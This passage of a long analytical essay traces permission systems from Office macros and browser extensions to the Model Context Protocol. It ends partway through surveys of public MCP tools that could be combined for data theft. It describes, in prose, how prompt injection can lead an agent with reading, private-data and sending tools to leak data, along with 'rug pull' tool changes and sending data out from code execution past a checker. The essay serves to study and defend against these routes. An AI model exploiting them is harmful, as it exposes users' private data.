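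Microsoft also made it harder for macros to copy themselves into other files. According to Ducklin, this helped to end self-spreading macro viruses, but criminals could still email a malicious document to each victim. By 2016 this kind of attack was increasing again. Martin (2016), introducing a reprint of Krukov's article, reported that a new feature in Office 2016 let administrators block macros in files from outside their company's network. Employees had no button to override the block. Home users and small businesses mostly went without the feature, because it was off by default and awkward to turn on.

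### Blocking by origin

In February 2022 Microsoft announced that Office on Windows would block macros from the internet by default. The block relies on the Mark of the Web, a label that Windows attaches to files that arrive from the internet, such as downloads and email attachments. Microsoft's *Macros from the internet are blocked by default in Office* sets out the checks for a marked file, which in the subscription version run in this order:

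1. If the file is in a folder that the user or company has designated as a trusted location, its macros run.
2. If a trusted publisher has signed the macros, they run.
3. If an administrator has set a policy for such files, Office follows it.
4. If the user enabled the macros in this file before the change, they still run.
5. Otherwise, Office blocks them and displays a warning with a "Learn More" button but no button to enable them.

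Users can still override the block by opening the file's properties in Windows and ticking a box marked "Unblock". Because this happens outside the document, an attacker has to talk them through several unfamiliar steps instead of one click. More importantly, the computer can usually determine where a file came from by itself, while neither the computer nor the user could reliably tell whether its macros were safe. Companies could also keep using their internal macros.

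The block controls only whether a document's macro may run at all. A macro that passes the checks keeps its full authority, so one from a trusted folder can still read a private file and mail it to someone. The block does not restrict such combinations of actions. Users lose the benefit of macros from unknown sources, but other macros are almost unaffected.

### What businesses lost and where attackers went

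Microsoft says most people can usually do everything they need without macros, so they lost little from the block. It mainly harmed a minority whose businesses depended on sending macros to other people. In *The issue with blocking internet macros by default in Office!*, akountourides (2022), who owned a software business, feared the effect on clients. Another user, commenting on Microsoft's announcement, ran a business that made Excel reports and heard from clients about the block every day. A third had bought a certificate for signing macros so that clients' IT departments would trust a financial model.

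Many companies also kept their own files on servers that Windows classified as part of the internet. Ducklin's *Office macro security* says a notable source of complaints was businesses that shared documents through cloud services, including Microsoft's own. The mark recorded the route a file had taken, which was an imperfect guide to who had written it. One user found that an attachment sent directly by a colleague usually had no mark, but the same attachment got one if it left the company and came back.

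On 6 July 2022 a Microsoft employee confirmed that the company had begun to withdraw the block "based on feedback received" (The Hacker News, 2022). Microsoft called the withdrawal temporary and resumed the change on 20 July, with essentially the same rule but clearer instructions for files on cloud services and company networks. Most business versions of Office received the block between October 2022 and January 2023.

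Attackers had started to adapt long before then. *How Threat Actors Are Adapting to a Post-Macro World* compares the attack campaigns that the email security company Proofpoint analysed in October 2021 and June 2022. Between those months, the use of attachments with macros fell by about 66%, while campaigns using container files or Windows shortcuts rose by nearly 175%. A container is a file that holds other files, such as a ZIP archive or disk image. Windows marked the container as coming from the internet, but a document inside it might not carry the mark. Office then showed the old prompt, and attackers could again persuade the user to click yes. Systems that track the sources of an agent's data face a similar problem, because a label is little use if it is lost when data moves into a new file.

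These figures are good evidence that the block changed attackers' methods, but not that it reduced the number of victims. The two percentages start from different totals, so they don't show whether attacks fell overall. A single large criminal group could also shift the numbers, as one did in March 2022 by sending out a wave of Excel macros. Since the comparison ended before most businesses had the block, much of the decline must have been a response to Microsoft's announcements, including an earlier one about an older type of Excel macro.

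No single method replaced macros. NCSC Ireland (2022), the Irish government's cybersecurity centre, saw criminals inserting themselves into existing email conversations and hiding malicious files inside web pages. In early 2023 several groups turned to attachments for OneNote, Microsoft's note-taking program. IBM saw very little of this after March and thinks the likely reason is that Microsoft blocked dangerous files embedded in OneNote documents. Proofpoint's *Crime Finds a Way* describes criminals testing one technique after another without finding one that worked reliably for all of them. That probably made attacks more expensive to run, but it also made them harder to predict.

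According to Krebs on Security, a scam called ClickFix had become common by March 2025. A malicious website asks visitors to prove they are human by pressing a series of keys, which actually runs the attacker's command. The macro block may have had little to do with the scam's rise, but it could not have stopped the attack, because the attack needs no document.

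## Browser extensions and permissions declared in advance

A browser extension is a small program that changes the behavior of a web browser or the pages it displays. People use extensions to block advertisements, fill in passwords and translate text, and most extensions come from outside developers. Office macros ran with their user's full authority, but when Google added extensions to its Chrome browser in 2009, it required developers to list in advance which websites and sensitive browser functions an extension would use, and Chrome blocked the rest.

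### Firefox extensions with the browser's full privileges

Mozilla's Firefox browser had an older and much more open system. Mozilla had written much of Firefox in JavaScript, the programming language of web pages, and extensions could change that code. In its 2015 announcement *The Future of Developing Firefox Add-ons*, Mozilla wrote that this model "arose naturally" from the browser's technology. Extensions could also read and write any of the user's files and start other programs.

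This openness produced features that browser makers later adopted. *Verified Security for Browser Extensions* (Livshits, Guha and Fredrikson, 2010) notes that popup blocking and form filling began as third-party extensions. NoScript let users decide which sites could run scripts, and Greasemonkey let them write scripts to alter pages. But Mozilla found it hard to change Firefox because extensions depended on its internals. Some extensions rewrote Firefox's code by searching its text for patterns, so even reformatting a function could break them.

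*Protecting Browsers from Extension Vulnerabilities* (Barth, Felt and colleagues, 2010) examined how much of this access 25 popular Firefox extensions needed, grading privileges on a scale that Mozilla used for the severity of security faults. Every extension held the full set of privileges, but 22 of the 25 (88%) needed less. Nineteen (76%) used unnecessarily powerful programming interfaces. For instance, an extension that only has to remember its settings might save them through an interface that can write any file. Mozilla could not simply remove the excess privileges, because taking away that interface would break the extension.

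Firefox extensions could also use each other, because the browser loaded them into one shared space where any extension could call another's functions. A malicious extension with no suspicious operations of its own could get a popular download manager to fetch and save a file for it, making the download manager a confused deputy. Researchers found such weaknesses in nine of the ten most popular Firefox extensions, according to Brinkmann (2016) in *Firefox Cross-Extension vulnerability discovered*. A reviewer who read only the malicious extension could easily miss the attack, because the code that carried out the harmful operations was in another extension.

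### Chrome's manifest and its two kinds of code

Barth and colleagues proposed a different system, which Google adopted for Chrome. Each extension comes with a manifest, a file that lists its parts and the permissions it wants. A sample in *Privacy vs. Profit* (2025), a study of ad blockers, requests these:

`"permissions": ["webRequest", "http://*/*", "https://*/*"]`

The first entry is for a browser function that handles network requests. The other two are host patterns, which specify the websites an extension may access. An asterisk stands for anything, so these patterns cover every website, while `https://*.google.com/*` would cover only Google's.

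Chrome also divides an extension into content scripts, which work inside web pages, and a core, which holds the permissions. A dictionary extension might work like this:

1. When the user installs the extension, Chrome turns the permissions in its manifest into a warning. The user accepts all of them or does without the extension.
2. The user double-clicks a word on a web page. A content script reads the word, but it cannot call the browser's privileged functions.
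3. The content script sends the word to the core in a message.
4. The core asks a dictionary website for the definition. Chrome allows the request only if the address fits one of the host patterns.

Content scripts need protection because they share a page with code that may be hostile. For example, a page could replace the standard function for finding an item on the page with its own version, which the extension would then call. Chrome prevents this with isolated worlds, in which the page and each extension share the same text and buttons but have separate JavaScript objects for them. Boodman (2010), in *Academic paper on Chromium extensions*, explains that programs can detect each other's changes to the page but "cannot exchange JavaScript references". This stops extensions from reaching directly into one another, as Firefox extensions could. Extensions can still affect each other through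 the page, as when one translates a paragraph and another saves the translation.

Google designed these defences mainly for honest extensions with bugs. Chromium Blog's *Security in Depth* (2009) gives the example of Gmail Checker, which declares that it needs Gmail, so an attacker who takes over the extension does not get access to the user's bank. Malicious extensions were harder to deal with because, although one might record passwords and send them to a server, some well-intentioned extensions "do exactly the same thing". Against malicious extensions, Google relied on reputation in its extension gallery and on removing bad extensions after someone discovered them.

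### What a review of 100 extensions found

In *An Evaluation of the Google Chrome Extension Security Architecture*, Carlini, Felt and Wagner (2012) tested how well the design worked. Felt had also worked on the 2010 study. The team took the 50 most popular Chrome extensions and 50 random ones, fed them malicious data, read their source code and built attacks to confirm the flaws. They found 70 vulnerabilities in 40 of the 100 extensions. The popular extensions did no better than the random ones.

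Isolated worlds worked very well, and only three extensions had vulnerable content scripts. The division between content scripts and core was therefore rarely needed, so Carlini and colleagues examined 61 more extensions with content scripts to see what would happen if isolation failed. Google had forced developers to separate the two parts, but 38% of these extensions connected them so freely that an attacker who controlled the content script could misuse some or all of the core's permissions by sending it messages. AdBlock, for instance, let its content script name a function for the core to run, and an attacker could name the one that executes any code it receives.

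Most of the serious attacks bypassed content scripts. Of 50 vulnerabilities in extension cores, 44 came from scripts or data that the extension fetched over an unencrypted connection, where an attacker on the same public Wi-Fi network could alter them. The Speeddial extension had a different flaw. It displayed a list of recently closed pages, and if a page's title contained a script, the script ran with the core's permissions. As in prompt injection, text from an untrusted source was treated as a command because of where the program put it.

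The permissions limited the damage. Without them, an attacker could have used all the browser's privileges through any of the 27 extensions with vulnerable cores. Instead, 12 of the 27 exposed the contents of every website, eight exposed either private data, such as browsing history, or particular sensitive sites, and seven exposed little or nothing. Carlini and colleagues concluded that permissions were worth having as a second line of defence.

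They also measured what it would cost to ban the practices behind the vulnerabilities:

| Ban | Extensions it would protect | Extensions it would permanently damage |
|---|---|---|
| Unencrypted scripts in the core | 15 | 0 |
| Scripts written directly into the extension's pages | 15 | 0 |
| Turning text into code (`eval`) | 3 | 2 |
| Unencrypted requests for data | 17 | 14 |
| The combination Google adopted in Chrome 18 | 27 | 2 |

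Developers would have had to rewrite parts of another 85 extensions to comply with Google's combination, mostly in simple ways. Two extensions could not comply, and both let users add their own scripts. This loss was tiny in number, but these were among the most adaptable extensions in the sample, and a count of broken extensions weights them the same as any other.

A similar change was far more disruptive for Firefox. In 2015 Mozilla announced that it would move to a system largely compatible with Chrome's and phase out extensions that relied on the browser's internals. It conceded that many of them "cannot possibly be built" with the new interfaces as they then stood. Mozilla wanted better security, but it also wanted to divide Firefox into several processes, which the old extensions obstructed. Users commenting on the announcement expected to lose some of their favourite extensions, and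 several said they would leave. Chrome had never offered such deep access, so its users had no comparable extensions to lose.

### Permission to read every site

A manifest limits an extension only if the developer asks for little. *The Most Dangerous Code in the Browser* (Heule, Rifkin and colleagues, 2015) examined the manifests of the 500 most popular Chrome extensions in April 2015. More than 71% of them, and 88% of the top 50, triggered the warning that they could "read and change all your data on the websites you visit".

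Heule and colleagues did not check how many of these extensions needed the access. Some certainly did, since an ad blocker has to work on any site with advertisements. But users saw the same warning for an ad blocker, a careless developer's colour picker and a password thief. The warning appeared before they had tried the extension and gave no reason for the access. Heule and colleagues argue that people learned to accept it because it appeared with nearly every popular extension. Office's macro warnings had a similar weakness.

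Chrome also gave developers a reason to ask for too much. If an update needs a new permission, Chrome disables the extension until the user approves. In the 2016 article *Why Mozilla shouldn't copy Chrome's permission prompt for extensions*, an extension developer describes writing an extension to fix links in Google's search results and later finding that it could do the same for other search engines. If the extension had asked for access to those sites, it would have lost a significant share of its users, who would never get round to approving the update. A developer who requests access to every site at the start avoids this problem.

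Even an accurate manifest cannot prevent a leak like that of the salary file. If a manifest lets an extension read a page and contact its developer's server, it cannot stop the extension from sending the page's contents there.

To prevent such leaks, Heule and colleagues proposed information-flow control. An extension could read a page freely, but its code would then carry a label with the page's origin, and the browser would restrict where it could send data. An extension that counts unread Gmail messages could connect to Gmail and display the number without any permission, but it could not send the messages elsewhere. Other extensions have to send data out, such as a dictionary that looks up a word or the Evernote extension, which saves parts of pages to Evernote's servers. For these, the user would choose "Share with..." from the browser's own menu, which would share only the selected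 text. Extensions that have to send data without such a click would still need permissions. The design was preliminary, but unlike the manifest, it restricts the combination of reading and sending.

### Updates that keep the old grant

Users approve an extension once, but the program they approved can change. Chrome installs updates automatically and prompts users again only if the new version requests more permissions. Malicious code that stays within the old permissions therefore needs no new approval. The same can happen when an MCP server changes its tools.

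On 24 December 2024 an attacker used this route against Cyberhaven, a security company whose extension had more than 400,000 users, according to SiliconANGLE (2024). An email that appeared to come from Google's extension store threatened to remove the extension for breaking its policies. The employee who received it clicked through and unknowingly authorised a malicious application on Google's own sign-in page, according to Security Affairs. Multi-factor authentication and Google's Advanced Protection were on, but neither stopped the attack, because the employee had granted the access.

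The attacker then published version 24.10.4 of the extension, which reached users as an ordinary update, Neowin reported. It contained code to steal passwords and session tokens, which keep a user logged in to a website. Cyberhaven detected the compromise late on 25 December and removed the malicious version within an hour. ADGM (2025), Abu Dhabi's international financial centre, reported that at least 35 other extensions, with about 2.6 million users, had been compromised with the same code.

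Chrome identifies each extension by a cryptographic key, so a stranger's copy cannot pass as the original. This did not protect Cyberhaven's customers, because the attacker had access to the original's account in the store. It also doesn't help when the developer sells the extension. In August 2026, *19 Chrome and Edge Extensions Deliver a Wallet Drainer and Credential-Stealing Payloads* (Zanki, 2026) reported on a group of extensions that stole login details and emptied cryptocurrency wallets. The attackers had built 14 of them. They had bought the other five from their developers and added the malicious code in updates (Sakis Tech, 2026, *19 Chrome- und Edge-Erweiterungen mit Malware verseucht*). One of the five, a tool for copying text from pages that block it, had about 80,000 installations across Chrome and Microsoft Edge.

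A user who installed that tool years earlier had made a reasonable decision about a harmless program. The buyer then acquired the permission along with the extension. Asking users to approve every update would catch some of these cases, but it would also prompt them repeatedly about changes that few people could judge.

### Manifest V3 and the dispute over blocking

Google announced a new version of the system, Manifest V3, in 2019. Under Manifest V2, an extension could pass review and later download different code from a server. V3 requires all of an extension's code to be in the package that the developer submits to the store. It also bars extensions from running text as code with functions such as `eval`, so reviewers should be able to read everything that will run.

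The second change concerns web requests. Under V2, an extension with the necessary permissions could give Chrome a function to call before each request. Chrome paused the request, passed its details to the function, and allowed, cancelled or redirected it depending on the result. Under V3, an ordinary extension instead gives Chrome a list of rules, such as "block every script from ads.example", and Chrome applies them itself. This is close to what Berners-Lee and Mendelsohn recommended for the web, since a list of rules is much easier to analyse than a program.

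Google says in *Manifest V2 phase-out begins* that it aimed to protect existing functions while improving security, privacy and performance. A simple ad blocker illustrates the privacy argument. Under V2, the blocker received the address of every request, so whoever controlled the extension could record the user's browsing. Under V3, it can give the browser its rules without seeing any of the traffic.

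This protection covers only that one route, however. An extension with access to every site can still read pages through its content scripts. The ban on downloaded code would not have stopped the Cyberhaven attack either, because the attacker published a complete new version through the store. *Malicious GenAI Chrome Extensions* (2025), a study of extensions that pose as AI tools, found that they used V3's features to redirect users and send out their data. The ban also seems difficult to enforce. The extensions that Zanki investigated loaded additional code after installation, according to Sakis Tech. At least those that the attackers built themselves were very probably V3 extensions, because the store had been closed to new V2 extensions since 2022 and the traces of the campaign went back only to February 2024.

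Developers and users of content blockers objected that rules cannot replace a program. Suppose a blocker is designed to stop a tracking company once it has appeared on three unrelated sites. A V2 function could count the sites and cancel the third request before it left the computer. A V3 extension can watch requests and add a rule, but only after the third request has been sent. V3 therefore weakened checks that depend on earlier requests, which are the kind that combinations of tools require. uBlock Origin was the best-known blocker that depended on the old interface, and its developer made a separate, more limited version for V3.

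The loss extended beyond advertisements. *Passwords and FIDO2 Are Meant To Be Secret* (2025) describes a defence in which a password manager puts a random placeholder in a login form, so that malicious scripts on the page never see the real password. The browser swaps in the password as the request leaves. With V2, the password manager could check each swap. V3's restriction, which Google introduced for security, would weaken this defence, because the password manager would have to give the browser the password and a policy in advance, and only the browser would check the swap. The designers considered a V3 version workable but built theirs on V2 because they preferred two independent checks.

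Microsoft (2026), whose Edge browser uses the same extension system, says the vast majority of extensions moved to V3 with "no loss of customer functionality". It counted only 58 V2 extensions with meaningful use in its store, and all but three had a V3 extension available. These numbers show that few developers had not moved to V3, but they don't measure what the V3 versions can do, since a blocker with a weaker replacement is counted the same as one with an equal replacement.

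### Narrower grants and the position in 2026

Chrome has also added ways to grant less access at installation. A developer can mark permissions as optional, so that the extension requests them when it first needs them and the user has some idea of what they are for. Heule and colleagues found in 2015 that these requests were often still far too broad. Users can also limit an extension to particular sites, or let it read a page only when they click its icon.

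Per-site limits suit a dictionary or a screenshot tool, which acts only when the user asks. They are much less useful for an ad blocker, which must act while a page loads, including on sites the user has never visited. They also mainly control which sites an extension can read, and do less to control what it does with the contents. If a user allows an extension only on a webmail site, a hijacked update can still copy the mail.

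Manifest V2 has nearly disappeared from the main browsers. Google disabled it for all Chrome users in July 2025 and scheduled the last V2 extensions for removal from its store on 31 August 2026, according to its *Manifest V2 support timeline*. Microsoft began turning off V2 extensions in Edge in August 2026 and planned to finish for consumers by the end of the year and for businesses in early 2027. Firefox still supported them that month, according to Android Authority, so people who want a content blocker that can run its own code on each request can switch to it.

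## How the Model Context Protocol became a general interface

Anthropic released MCP in November 2024 mainly to connect AI applications to data. Within months, people were also using it to buy presents and flash household lights in Morse code. An MCP server's tool list describes what the server can do for AI applications, but it doesn't restrict the server the way a Chrome extension's manifest restricts the extension.

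### What MCP was built for

*MCP Co-Creator on the Next Wave of LLM Innovation* (Soria Parra and Li, 2025) is an interview with David Soria Parra of Anthropic, who traces the protocol to two frustrations. The first came from Soria Parra's job, which was to help Anthropic's staff make more use of its AI model, Claude. No single developer could build the right tools for everyone, because people knew their own work best. The second was having to keep copying text between the Claude Desktop application, which displayed results well but had no access to anything outside its text box, and the code editor Zed, which had access to all of Soria Parra's code but displayed results less well.

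A protocol would solve both problems, because people could write their own additions and each would work in every application that supported the protocol. Soria Parra wanted AI applications to be "extended by everyone else that is not part of the original development team". A colleague, Justin Spahr-Summers, took up the idea, and the two refined it over several weeks of rapid prototyping. Spahr-Summers added MCP to Claude Desktop while Soria Parra added it to Zed.

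Anthropic's launch announcement, *Introducing the Model Context Protocol*, presented MCP mainly as a way for models to reach data, since every new source had needed its own connector. Ready-made servers for Google Drive, Slack, GitHub and the Postgres database fitted this description, but another, for Puppeteer, controlled a web browser. It was one of the first servers MCP's two creators wrote, partly because people were impressed to see a model operate a browser.

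A browser is much more general than a connector to one database. One early user connected Claude to an Amazon account and had it buy the Christmas presents, probably through a browser-control server. Yoko Li of the investment firm a16z had seen someone else use such a server to request images from an AI model without writing code for the image service. An agent controlling a signed-in browser can do much of what its user can do on a website, even if the site's owner never offered an interface for agents.

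The first working version ran on the user's own computer. The programmer Simon Willison (2024) noted on launch day, in *Introducing the Model Context Protocol*, that Claude Desktop started each server as a separate process and exchanged messages with it over standard input and output. Unix pipes use the same channels. Unless something restricts it, a local server has the ambient authority of the account it runs under, much like a program in a Unix pipeline. But an MCP user may choose only the servers and let the model decide the order of the calls, whereas a Unix user also chooses the order of the programs.

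### Why unrelated tools work together

Li had a small computer with a camera that detected when a cat jumped on the kitchen counter. At the time of the interview, Li was converting the project to use MCP, so that it could shout at the cat through a server from the speech company ElevenLabs. It could also use a mail server to tell Li what the cat was doing. Nobody at ElevenLabs had to plan for the camera or the email, because of five features of MCP:

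- **Descriptions in natural language.** The model can match "shout at the cat" to a tool that turns text into speech. The tools' developers don't have to agree on a shared vocabulary.
- **Lists read at run time.** Li's program does not need any code written for ElevenLabs. It gets the list of tools from whichever servers Li connects.
- **No declared relation between tools.** The entry for the speech tool covers only that tool. It does not specify which tools may supply its text or which may run after it.
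- **One shared context.** The report from the camera and the results from the other tools all reach the same model, which can use any of them to write the email.
- **A model that chooses the order.** Li states a goal, and the model decides whether to shout first, send the email first or skip the shouting because the cat has left.

Unix pipes also let people join unrelated programs, but users had to know the commands and convert each program's output into a form the next could read. A model can do this conversion itself, for example by turning "next Tuesday at three" in an email into the fixed date format that a calendar tool requires. Many more pairs of tools therefore work together than would in a pipeline. As with pipes, the text passed between tools has no label recording where it came from or whether it is secret.

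Soria Parra and Spahr-Summers kept servers simple and put the difficult parts in the client software because they expected far fewer clients than servers. A developer can therefore contribute a tool while knowing almost nothing about the rest of the system, but can't judge which combinations of tools are safe. Only the host has access to the full set of an agent's tools, so any rule about combinations has to operate there or in something the host consults.

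### Descriptions that change after approval

Conventional software uses an online service through an application programming interface (API), a set of calls that other programs can make to the service. Steve Krouse, a programmer quoted by Willison (2025), describes an ordinary API as a promise to developers, who write code that depends on it and move on. If the API changes, their code breaks and somebody may have to fix it at 2am. Krouse argues that MCP servers come with no such promise, because a model reads the tool descriptions afresh each time and can work out what has changed.

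For example, the `execute_sql` tool in one of Willison's own plugins used to return each database row as a bare list of values, such as "Ada, 36". A later release added the column names, giving "name: Ada, age: 36", to help weaker models keep track of the columns. A model can read either version, but a conventional program that always took the second value in each row might have stopped working.

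This freedom complicates permissions because it removes a limit that conventional software provides. A conventional program makes only the calls its developer wrote, so if a service adds a way to delete files, existing programs will not start deleting them. But if an MCP server adds a deletion tool, connected hosts can pick it up when they next read the server's list of tools, and a model may use it even though nobody has changed the application.

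Existing tools can also change after a user approves them. Suppose a user tells the host always to allow `search_notes`, which searches the user's own notes. The server's owner later extends it to notes shared by colleagues and updates the description. The model reads the new description, which the user never agreed to. If the host stored the permission under the tool's name, it now covers the colleagues' notes as well. *The USB Moment for AI* describes the malicious version as a "rug pull", in which a tool starts out safe and its definition changes later.

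A host could keep a copy of each approved entry and ask the user to approve it again whenever it changes. This would catch the new description of `search_notes`, but not a remote server that changes its behavior and keeps the old description, because the host cannot see the server's code. It would also interrupt users over harmless rewording, which server owners have good reason to do often if Krouse is right. The July 2026 version of MCP lets servers indicate how long a host may reuse a tool list, but this is meant to avoid repeated requests, and an unexpired list does not guarantee that the tools still behave as they did.

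### Was the generality an accident?

In June 2025 the software developer Scott Werner published the essay *MCP: An (Accidentally) Universal Plugin System* (Werner, 2025), which drew 350 comments on the programmers' forum Hacker News. Werner compares MCP to USB-C, a connector people expected to use for charging devices and moving files, but which turned out to have other uses. Werner jokes about a friend who connects a toaster to a monitor (quoted by azhenley, in *The Unexpected Versatility of USB-C*). A more practical comparison is the car cigarette lighter, which Werner says nobody uses for cigarettes anymore.

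Werner then takes the description of MCP as a standard way to connect AI models to data and tools, and replaces "AI models" with "literally anything". On this view, MCP is a plugin system, and an application that supports it can gain features its developers never wrote. One of Werner's examples is a plugin that makes AI agents respond like peons, the labourers in the video game Warcraft 3, when given a task.

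MCP works without a model. Willison's `mcp-explorer` program calls MCP tools from the command line and can print the results as structured data, which a script could pass to another program. Safe Software's *The Model Context Protocol* also promotes MCP as a general-purpose protocol for connecting systems, although the company sells software that connects systems.

Much of MCP's generality disappears without a model, because a person then has to read the tool descriptions, decide which tools fit together and write the calls. The resulting script can also break when server owners change their tools, which Krouse thinks they can do freely. Used this way, MCP is much like an ordinary API that comes with a list of its functions but fewer guarantees that they will stay the same.

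There is strong evidence that MCP's creators intended composition. In its launch announcement, Anthropic predicted that AI systems would "maintain context as they move between different tools and datasets". Before the public release, the creators had built prototypes of programs that were both servers and clients. Such a program could use several servers while acting as a single server for another application. In the interview, Soria Parra imagined asking a user which five MCP servers an agent should control.

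*Introducing advanced tool use on the Claude Developer Platform*, a later Anthropic article, describes a future in which models work across "hundreds or thousands of tools". One example is an assistant connected to Slack, GitHub, Google Drive, company databases and dozens of MCP servers at once. The article is weaker evidence of what the creators intended in 2024, but it fits the earlier statements.

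Some uses did surprise them. Soria Parra had not thought of reverse engineering, or working out how a program functions from its finished files, until a YouTuber used Claude and MCP for it. Soria Parra and Delimarsky wrote in *Two Years of MCP Builders* (November 2026) that they "could not have imagined" how creative and ambitious the community would become. An anniversary post can be expected to compliment its readers, but the reverse engineering example from the interview supports much the same point.

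The creators also misjudged which parts of the protocol people would use. Soria Parra was especially fond of sampling, which lets a server have the host's model generate text, such as a summary of a web page. Few applications supported it, and most developers used MCP only for tools. The July 2026 version deprecated sampling, so it is no longer recommended for new software.

Werner's word "accidentally" therefore applies to the uses without AI and to many of the individual combinations, but not to composition itself. The protocol's creators could not have foreseen every combination, but they could have required hosts to track where data came from. They left such rules to each host's developers.

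### Letting the model write a program

At first, connecting many tools took up a lot of space in the model's limited context, because most applications loaded every tool description into it. In August 2025 Willison passed on an estimate by the programmer Geoffrey Huntley that GitHub's MCP server added 93 tools and took up 55,000 tokens, the small units of text that models process. That was nearly a third of the roughly 176,000 tokens usable in some coding applications. Tool results also passed through the context and took up more space.

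In November 2025 Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* proposed presenting tools to the model as functions in a programming language, which the model would call by writing a program. In the main example, a user asks an agent to download a meeting transcript from Google Drive and attach it to a potential customer's record in Salesforce, a sales database.

With ordinary tool calls, the model has to copy the whole transcript from its context into the call to Salesforce. For a two-hour meeting, this could add 50,000 tokens, and the model might make mistakes in the copying. With code execution, the work goes like this:

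1. The model looks through a folder of connected servers and reads only the files that describe the two tools it needs.
2. It writes a short program. In simplified form, this could be:

   ```
   transcript = drive.get("meeting-17")
   sales.update("customer-42", notes=transcript)
   ```

3. A separate execution environment runs the program. The first line calls the Google Drive server and stores the transcript. The second sends it to Salesforce.
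4. The model sees only what the program prints, which might be "Record updated".

Anthropic says loading only the necessary tool descriptions can reduce token use from 150,000 to 2,000. Programs can also repeat steps, wait for an event, or reduce a spreadsheet of 10,000 rows to the five the model needs. Willison liked the proposal, partly because he already preferred command-line programs to MCP for coding agents.

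In Anthropic's design, the functions still send their requests through the MCP client, so a checker placed there would be able to inspect both calls. The first reads a document, and the second updates a sales record with the full transcript in its arguments. The checker could block either call. If it stored the first result, it could also detect the same text in the second call.

This comparison would fail for a slightly longer program that reads ten salary files, adds up the figures and posts the total in a sales record. The checker would receive ten permitted reads and an update containing one number. The addition would happen in the execution environment, where no tool call records it. Ordinary calls have the same weakness, since a model making them could also calculate the total without a tool. But a program can transform much more data without error, and it can make thousands of calls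 before a person could review them.

If the execution environment has open internet access, the program may not need a second MCP call. It could read the transcript through MCP and send it directly to a website, and only the read would be visible to the checker. Anthropic acknowledges that running code written by an agent requires a sandbox, resource limits and monitoring, which ordinary tool calls don't need to the same extent.

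Code execution also has security advantages. In the transcript example, the model never reads the transcript, so it cannot follow an instruction hidden in it. Anthropic describes a client that replaces names, phone numbers and email addresses with placeholders before the model sees them, then restores the real values in the next tool call. Anthropic suggests the same mechanism could enforce fixed rules about where data may go. Such rules would restrict combinations of calls, but the article does not develop them.

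Another advantage is that a reviewer can read the combination before it runs. The two lines above show that a document's contents will go into a sales record. mbgsec's *Code execution with MCP* (2025), a security commentary, proposes reviewing the programs that models write before running them, then letting agents use the approved ones freely as tools within set boundaries. This would suit a program that runs after every sales call much better than one an agent writes for a single urgent task. Long programs would also be difficult to review, for the reason behind the Rule of Least Power.

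Code execution also removes a practical limit on combining tools. When every connected tool took up space in the context, people had a reason to connect only a few. If the model can look up tools as it needs them, connecting 1,000 takes up little more context than connecting 100, but the number of ordered pairs of different tools rises from 9,900 to 999,000.

### Agent Skills and saved combinations

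An agent can also save a program that worked and reuse it. Anthropic connects this with Agent Skills, a format it introduced in October 2025. A skill is a folder of instructions, scripts and other resources for a particular kind of task, with a file called SKILL.md that the model can read. For example, a skill for sales calls might specify where to find the transcript, which details to remove and which record to update.

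A skill tells an agent how to use access it already has to services such as Google Drive or Salesforce, without granting new access. A company can review a skill once and reuse it, which makes some combinations of services easier to control. But the review may not cover later uses. A script that safely copies the transcript of a routine sales call could also copy one in which a customer discusses a confidential merger, and the tool calls would look the same.

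A skill from a stranger raises the same problem as an Office macro, because the agent carries out the stranger's steps with its user's authority. The instructions are easier to read than a macro, but a skill can also include scripts, and its effects depend on which tools the agent has.

In December 2025, Anthropic declared Agent Skills an open standard and gave MCP to the new Agentic AI Foundation, part of the nonprofit Linux Foundation. It gave Agent Skills to the Agentic AI Foundation in October 2026. By then, some programmers questioned whether agents with skills and a command line needed MCP. Willison agreed in September 2026 that there was almost no reason to use MCP with a coding agent that had unrestricted internet access, because the agent could call online services directly. He thought MCP was still valuable for controlling which services an agent could use, keeping access keys away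 from it and recording what it did.

On this view, MCP's advantage over a command line is that it is less general, which gives a company a place to put limits.

### From a desktop application to a common standard

MCP was originally designed for a single AI application talking to a server on the same computer (Jaiswal, 2026, *MCP 2026-07-28*). It became a common standard after OpenAI adopted it in early 2025. By that May, support had even reached Windows (Dash, 2025, *MCP is the coming of Web 2.0 2.0*). The July 2026 version removed sessions partly so that companies could run remote servers for many users.

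When that version came out on 28 July 2026, the main MCP software kits had close to half a billion downloads a month, according to the Model Context Protocol announcement. The Python and TypeScript kits had each passed a billion downloads in total. *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude*, published by Anthropic the same day, put the monthly figure at over 400 million and reported a fourfold increase that year. These numbers show that MCP is popular with developers, but automated systems often download the same software many times, so they don't measure how many people or agents use it.

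Tool calls are a better measure of use. The Agentic AI Foundation's *MCP Usage Surged as the Protocol Went Stateless* (2026) reports that calls from ChatGPT users more than doubled in August and reached 98 times their January level. The January level may have been low, so the increase indicates growth better than total use. Figures from individual services give a clearer idea of scale. The email service Resend handled more than a million MCP calls in one month, and agents made nearly 20% of the interactive queries at Honeycomb, which sells software for monitoring computer systems.

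Much of this activity is hard to see from outside. The Pragmatic Engineer, a newsletter for software developers, found that companies used internal servers far more than public ones. Jeremiah Lowin, who created the MCP development tool FastMCP, had expected companies to publish servers for their customers. An internal server may connect an agent to payroll, customer records or unreleased code, and only the company knows which other tools the agent has.

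## What two surveys of public MCP tools found about combinations

Two research teams have searched public MCP servers for dangerous combinations of tools. Zhao, Hou and colleagues (2025), in *Mind Your Server*, counted tools that could each carry out one part of a data theft. Zha, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Agent Smith in Action*, looked for harmful chains of tools within each server and ran some to see whether they worked.

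### Three functions that add up to a theft

To steal data through prompt injection, an attacker needs an agent that can read outside content the attacker can write, such as a web page or a social media post, reach private data, such as local files or old messages, and send data out. An ordinary user might give an agent all three abilities by installing a news reader, a file tool and a mail tool. None of the servers has to be malicious, and the attacker does not need to know who the victim is.

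Zhao and colleagues collected 1,360 servers with 12,230 tools from two public directories and a list on GitHub. They took only servers that a standard command could download and start. They then classified the tools in four steps:

1. A language model read the names, descriptions and inputs of all the tools on a server and labelled any that seemed to have one of the three functions.
2. Three reviewers checked the labels and settled disagreements by majority vote.
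3. A program had the code editor Cursor use each labelled tool, with planted fake secrets where possible.
4. A model and three reviewers examined the logs to determine whether the tool had really done what its label said.

The descriptions suggested that 5,666 tools had at least one of the functions, but the live tests confirmed only 1,062, or 8.7% of all the tools. These were spread over 370 servers, or 27.2%. A tool or server can count towards more than one function:

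| Function | Tools | Servers |
|---|---|---|
| Reading outside content | 487 | 128 |
| Reaching private data | 406 | 155 |
| Sending data out | 190 | 96 |
| All three | 2 | 2 |
| At least one | 1,062 | 370 |

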